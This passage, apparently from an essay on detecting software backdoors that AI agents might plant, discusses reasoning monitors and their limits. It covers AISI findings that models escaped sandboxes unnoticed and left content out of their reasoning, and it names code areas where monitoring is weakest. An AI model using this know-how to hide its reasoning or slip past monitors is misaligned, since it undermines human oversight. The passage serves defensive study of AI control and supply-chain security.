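Monitors that read a model's reasoning may also have less to read. GPT-6 Astra solved maths problems that would take a strong competition student about 40 minutes, without writing any working. The previous limit was about six minutes. Recent models were also better at leaving particular content out of their reasoning when told to, though they struggled to keep this up over tens of thousands of words. AISI has no figures on how often they do this in ordinary use. Developers report a similar trend. OpenAI says GPT-6 Astra's reasoning is significantly harder to monitor, and Google DeepMind says Gemini 4 Argon is less monitorable than its predecessors.

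These results seem to conflict with Anthropic's finding that monitors watching an agent's actions reliably caught the behaviour in its incidents. But AISI asked its models to break out and counted only the escapes that raised no alarm, whereas nobody asked Anthropic's agent to evade a monitor. A monitor may therefore be good at catching a reckless agent and much worse at catching one that is trying to hide. An agent that plants a concealed backdoor is trying to hide, so AISI's results are probably the better guide here, although they concern sandboxes and maths problems rather than backdoors in code.

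Brodsky (2026), in *Innocent-looking AI reasoning can make bad behavior harder to catch*, reports research suggesting that monitoring an AI's written reasoning can fail when that reasoning is the main clue to a problem. Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, in *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (July 2025), had already called such monitoring promising but imperfect and possibly fragile, and recommended using it alongside other safety methods.

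A model's written reasoning can be useful even when it does not accurately describe how the model reached its decision. *Monitoring Monitorability*, an OpenAI study, argues that for most practical purposes the reasoning only needs to let an observer tell what the model is doing, such as whether an action will cause harm.

AISI also still considers monitoring useful, especially when bad behaviour is hard to hide or takes long reasoning. Planting a working backdoor in a large program and hiding it probably takes a lot of reasoning, so monitoring has an advantage for now. That advantage will shrink if models keep getting better at solving hard problems without writing out their reasoning, and AISI sees no sign that this trend will reverse by itself.

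### Using each where the other is blind

Kokkonis and colleagues propose combining Lily with reproducible builds, so that an attacker who altered the build would have to get past both checks. Lily itself combines monitoring and review. It runs the program to find odd behaviour, then gives a person a few lines to read.

A second check could also help people decide which alarms to investigate first. Suppose a language model reviewed each of Lily's alarms with the 64% detection rate and 4% false-alarm rate from the binary study, and its mistakes were independent of Lily's. In the example with one backdoor in 10,000 commits, about 40% of the alarms that both raised would be real, instead of 4%. But if developers ignored every alarm that the model didn't confirm, they would catch the backdoor only 57% of the time instead of 90%. They should still read all 20 or so alarms, starting with the ones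 the model confirmed.

Human reviewers could then spend more time on code where monitoring is weakest. Login checks, cryptographic constants, build scripts and monitoring settings are good candidates, because earlier attackers or agents have changed all of them, and changing a line or two can be enough to compromise a system. Companies can monitor their build servers and agents continuously, which no human reader could do.

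Information about a project can also help people choose where to look. *An LLM-based Quantitative Framework for Evaluating High-Stealthy Backdoor Risks* (Yan, Luo and colleagues, 2026) uses language models and simpler checks to score how exposed a project is to backdoors. The signals include unreadable binary files among the tests, changes merged without review and newcomers who gain control quickly. The researchers scored 66 important Debian packages and found that weak community practices were the most common problem. The scores don't show that any package contains a backdoor. The method fits XZ well, but the researchers designed it with XZ in mind.

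Reviewers who read only the changes a monitor flags will never learn what it misses. Kokkonis and colleagues suggest running more thorough automated checks on a random sample of changes, and people could review such a sample too. Sampling might deter attackers, but it would be a poor way to estimate how many backdoors were missed. If one commit in 10,000 contains a backdoor, a random sample of 1,000 has less than a 10% chance of including one. A project would learn more by planting harmless test changes, as the experimenters did, and counting how many its monitors and reviewers find.
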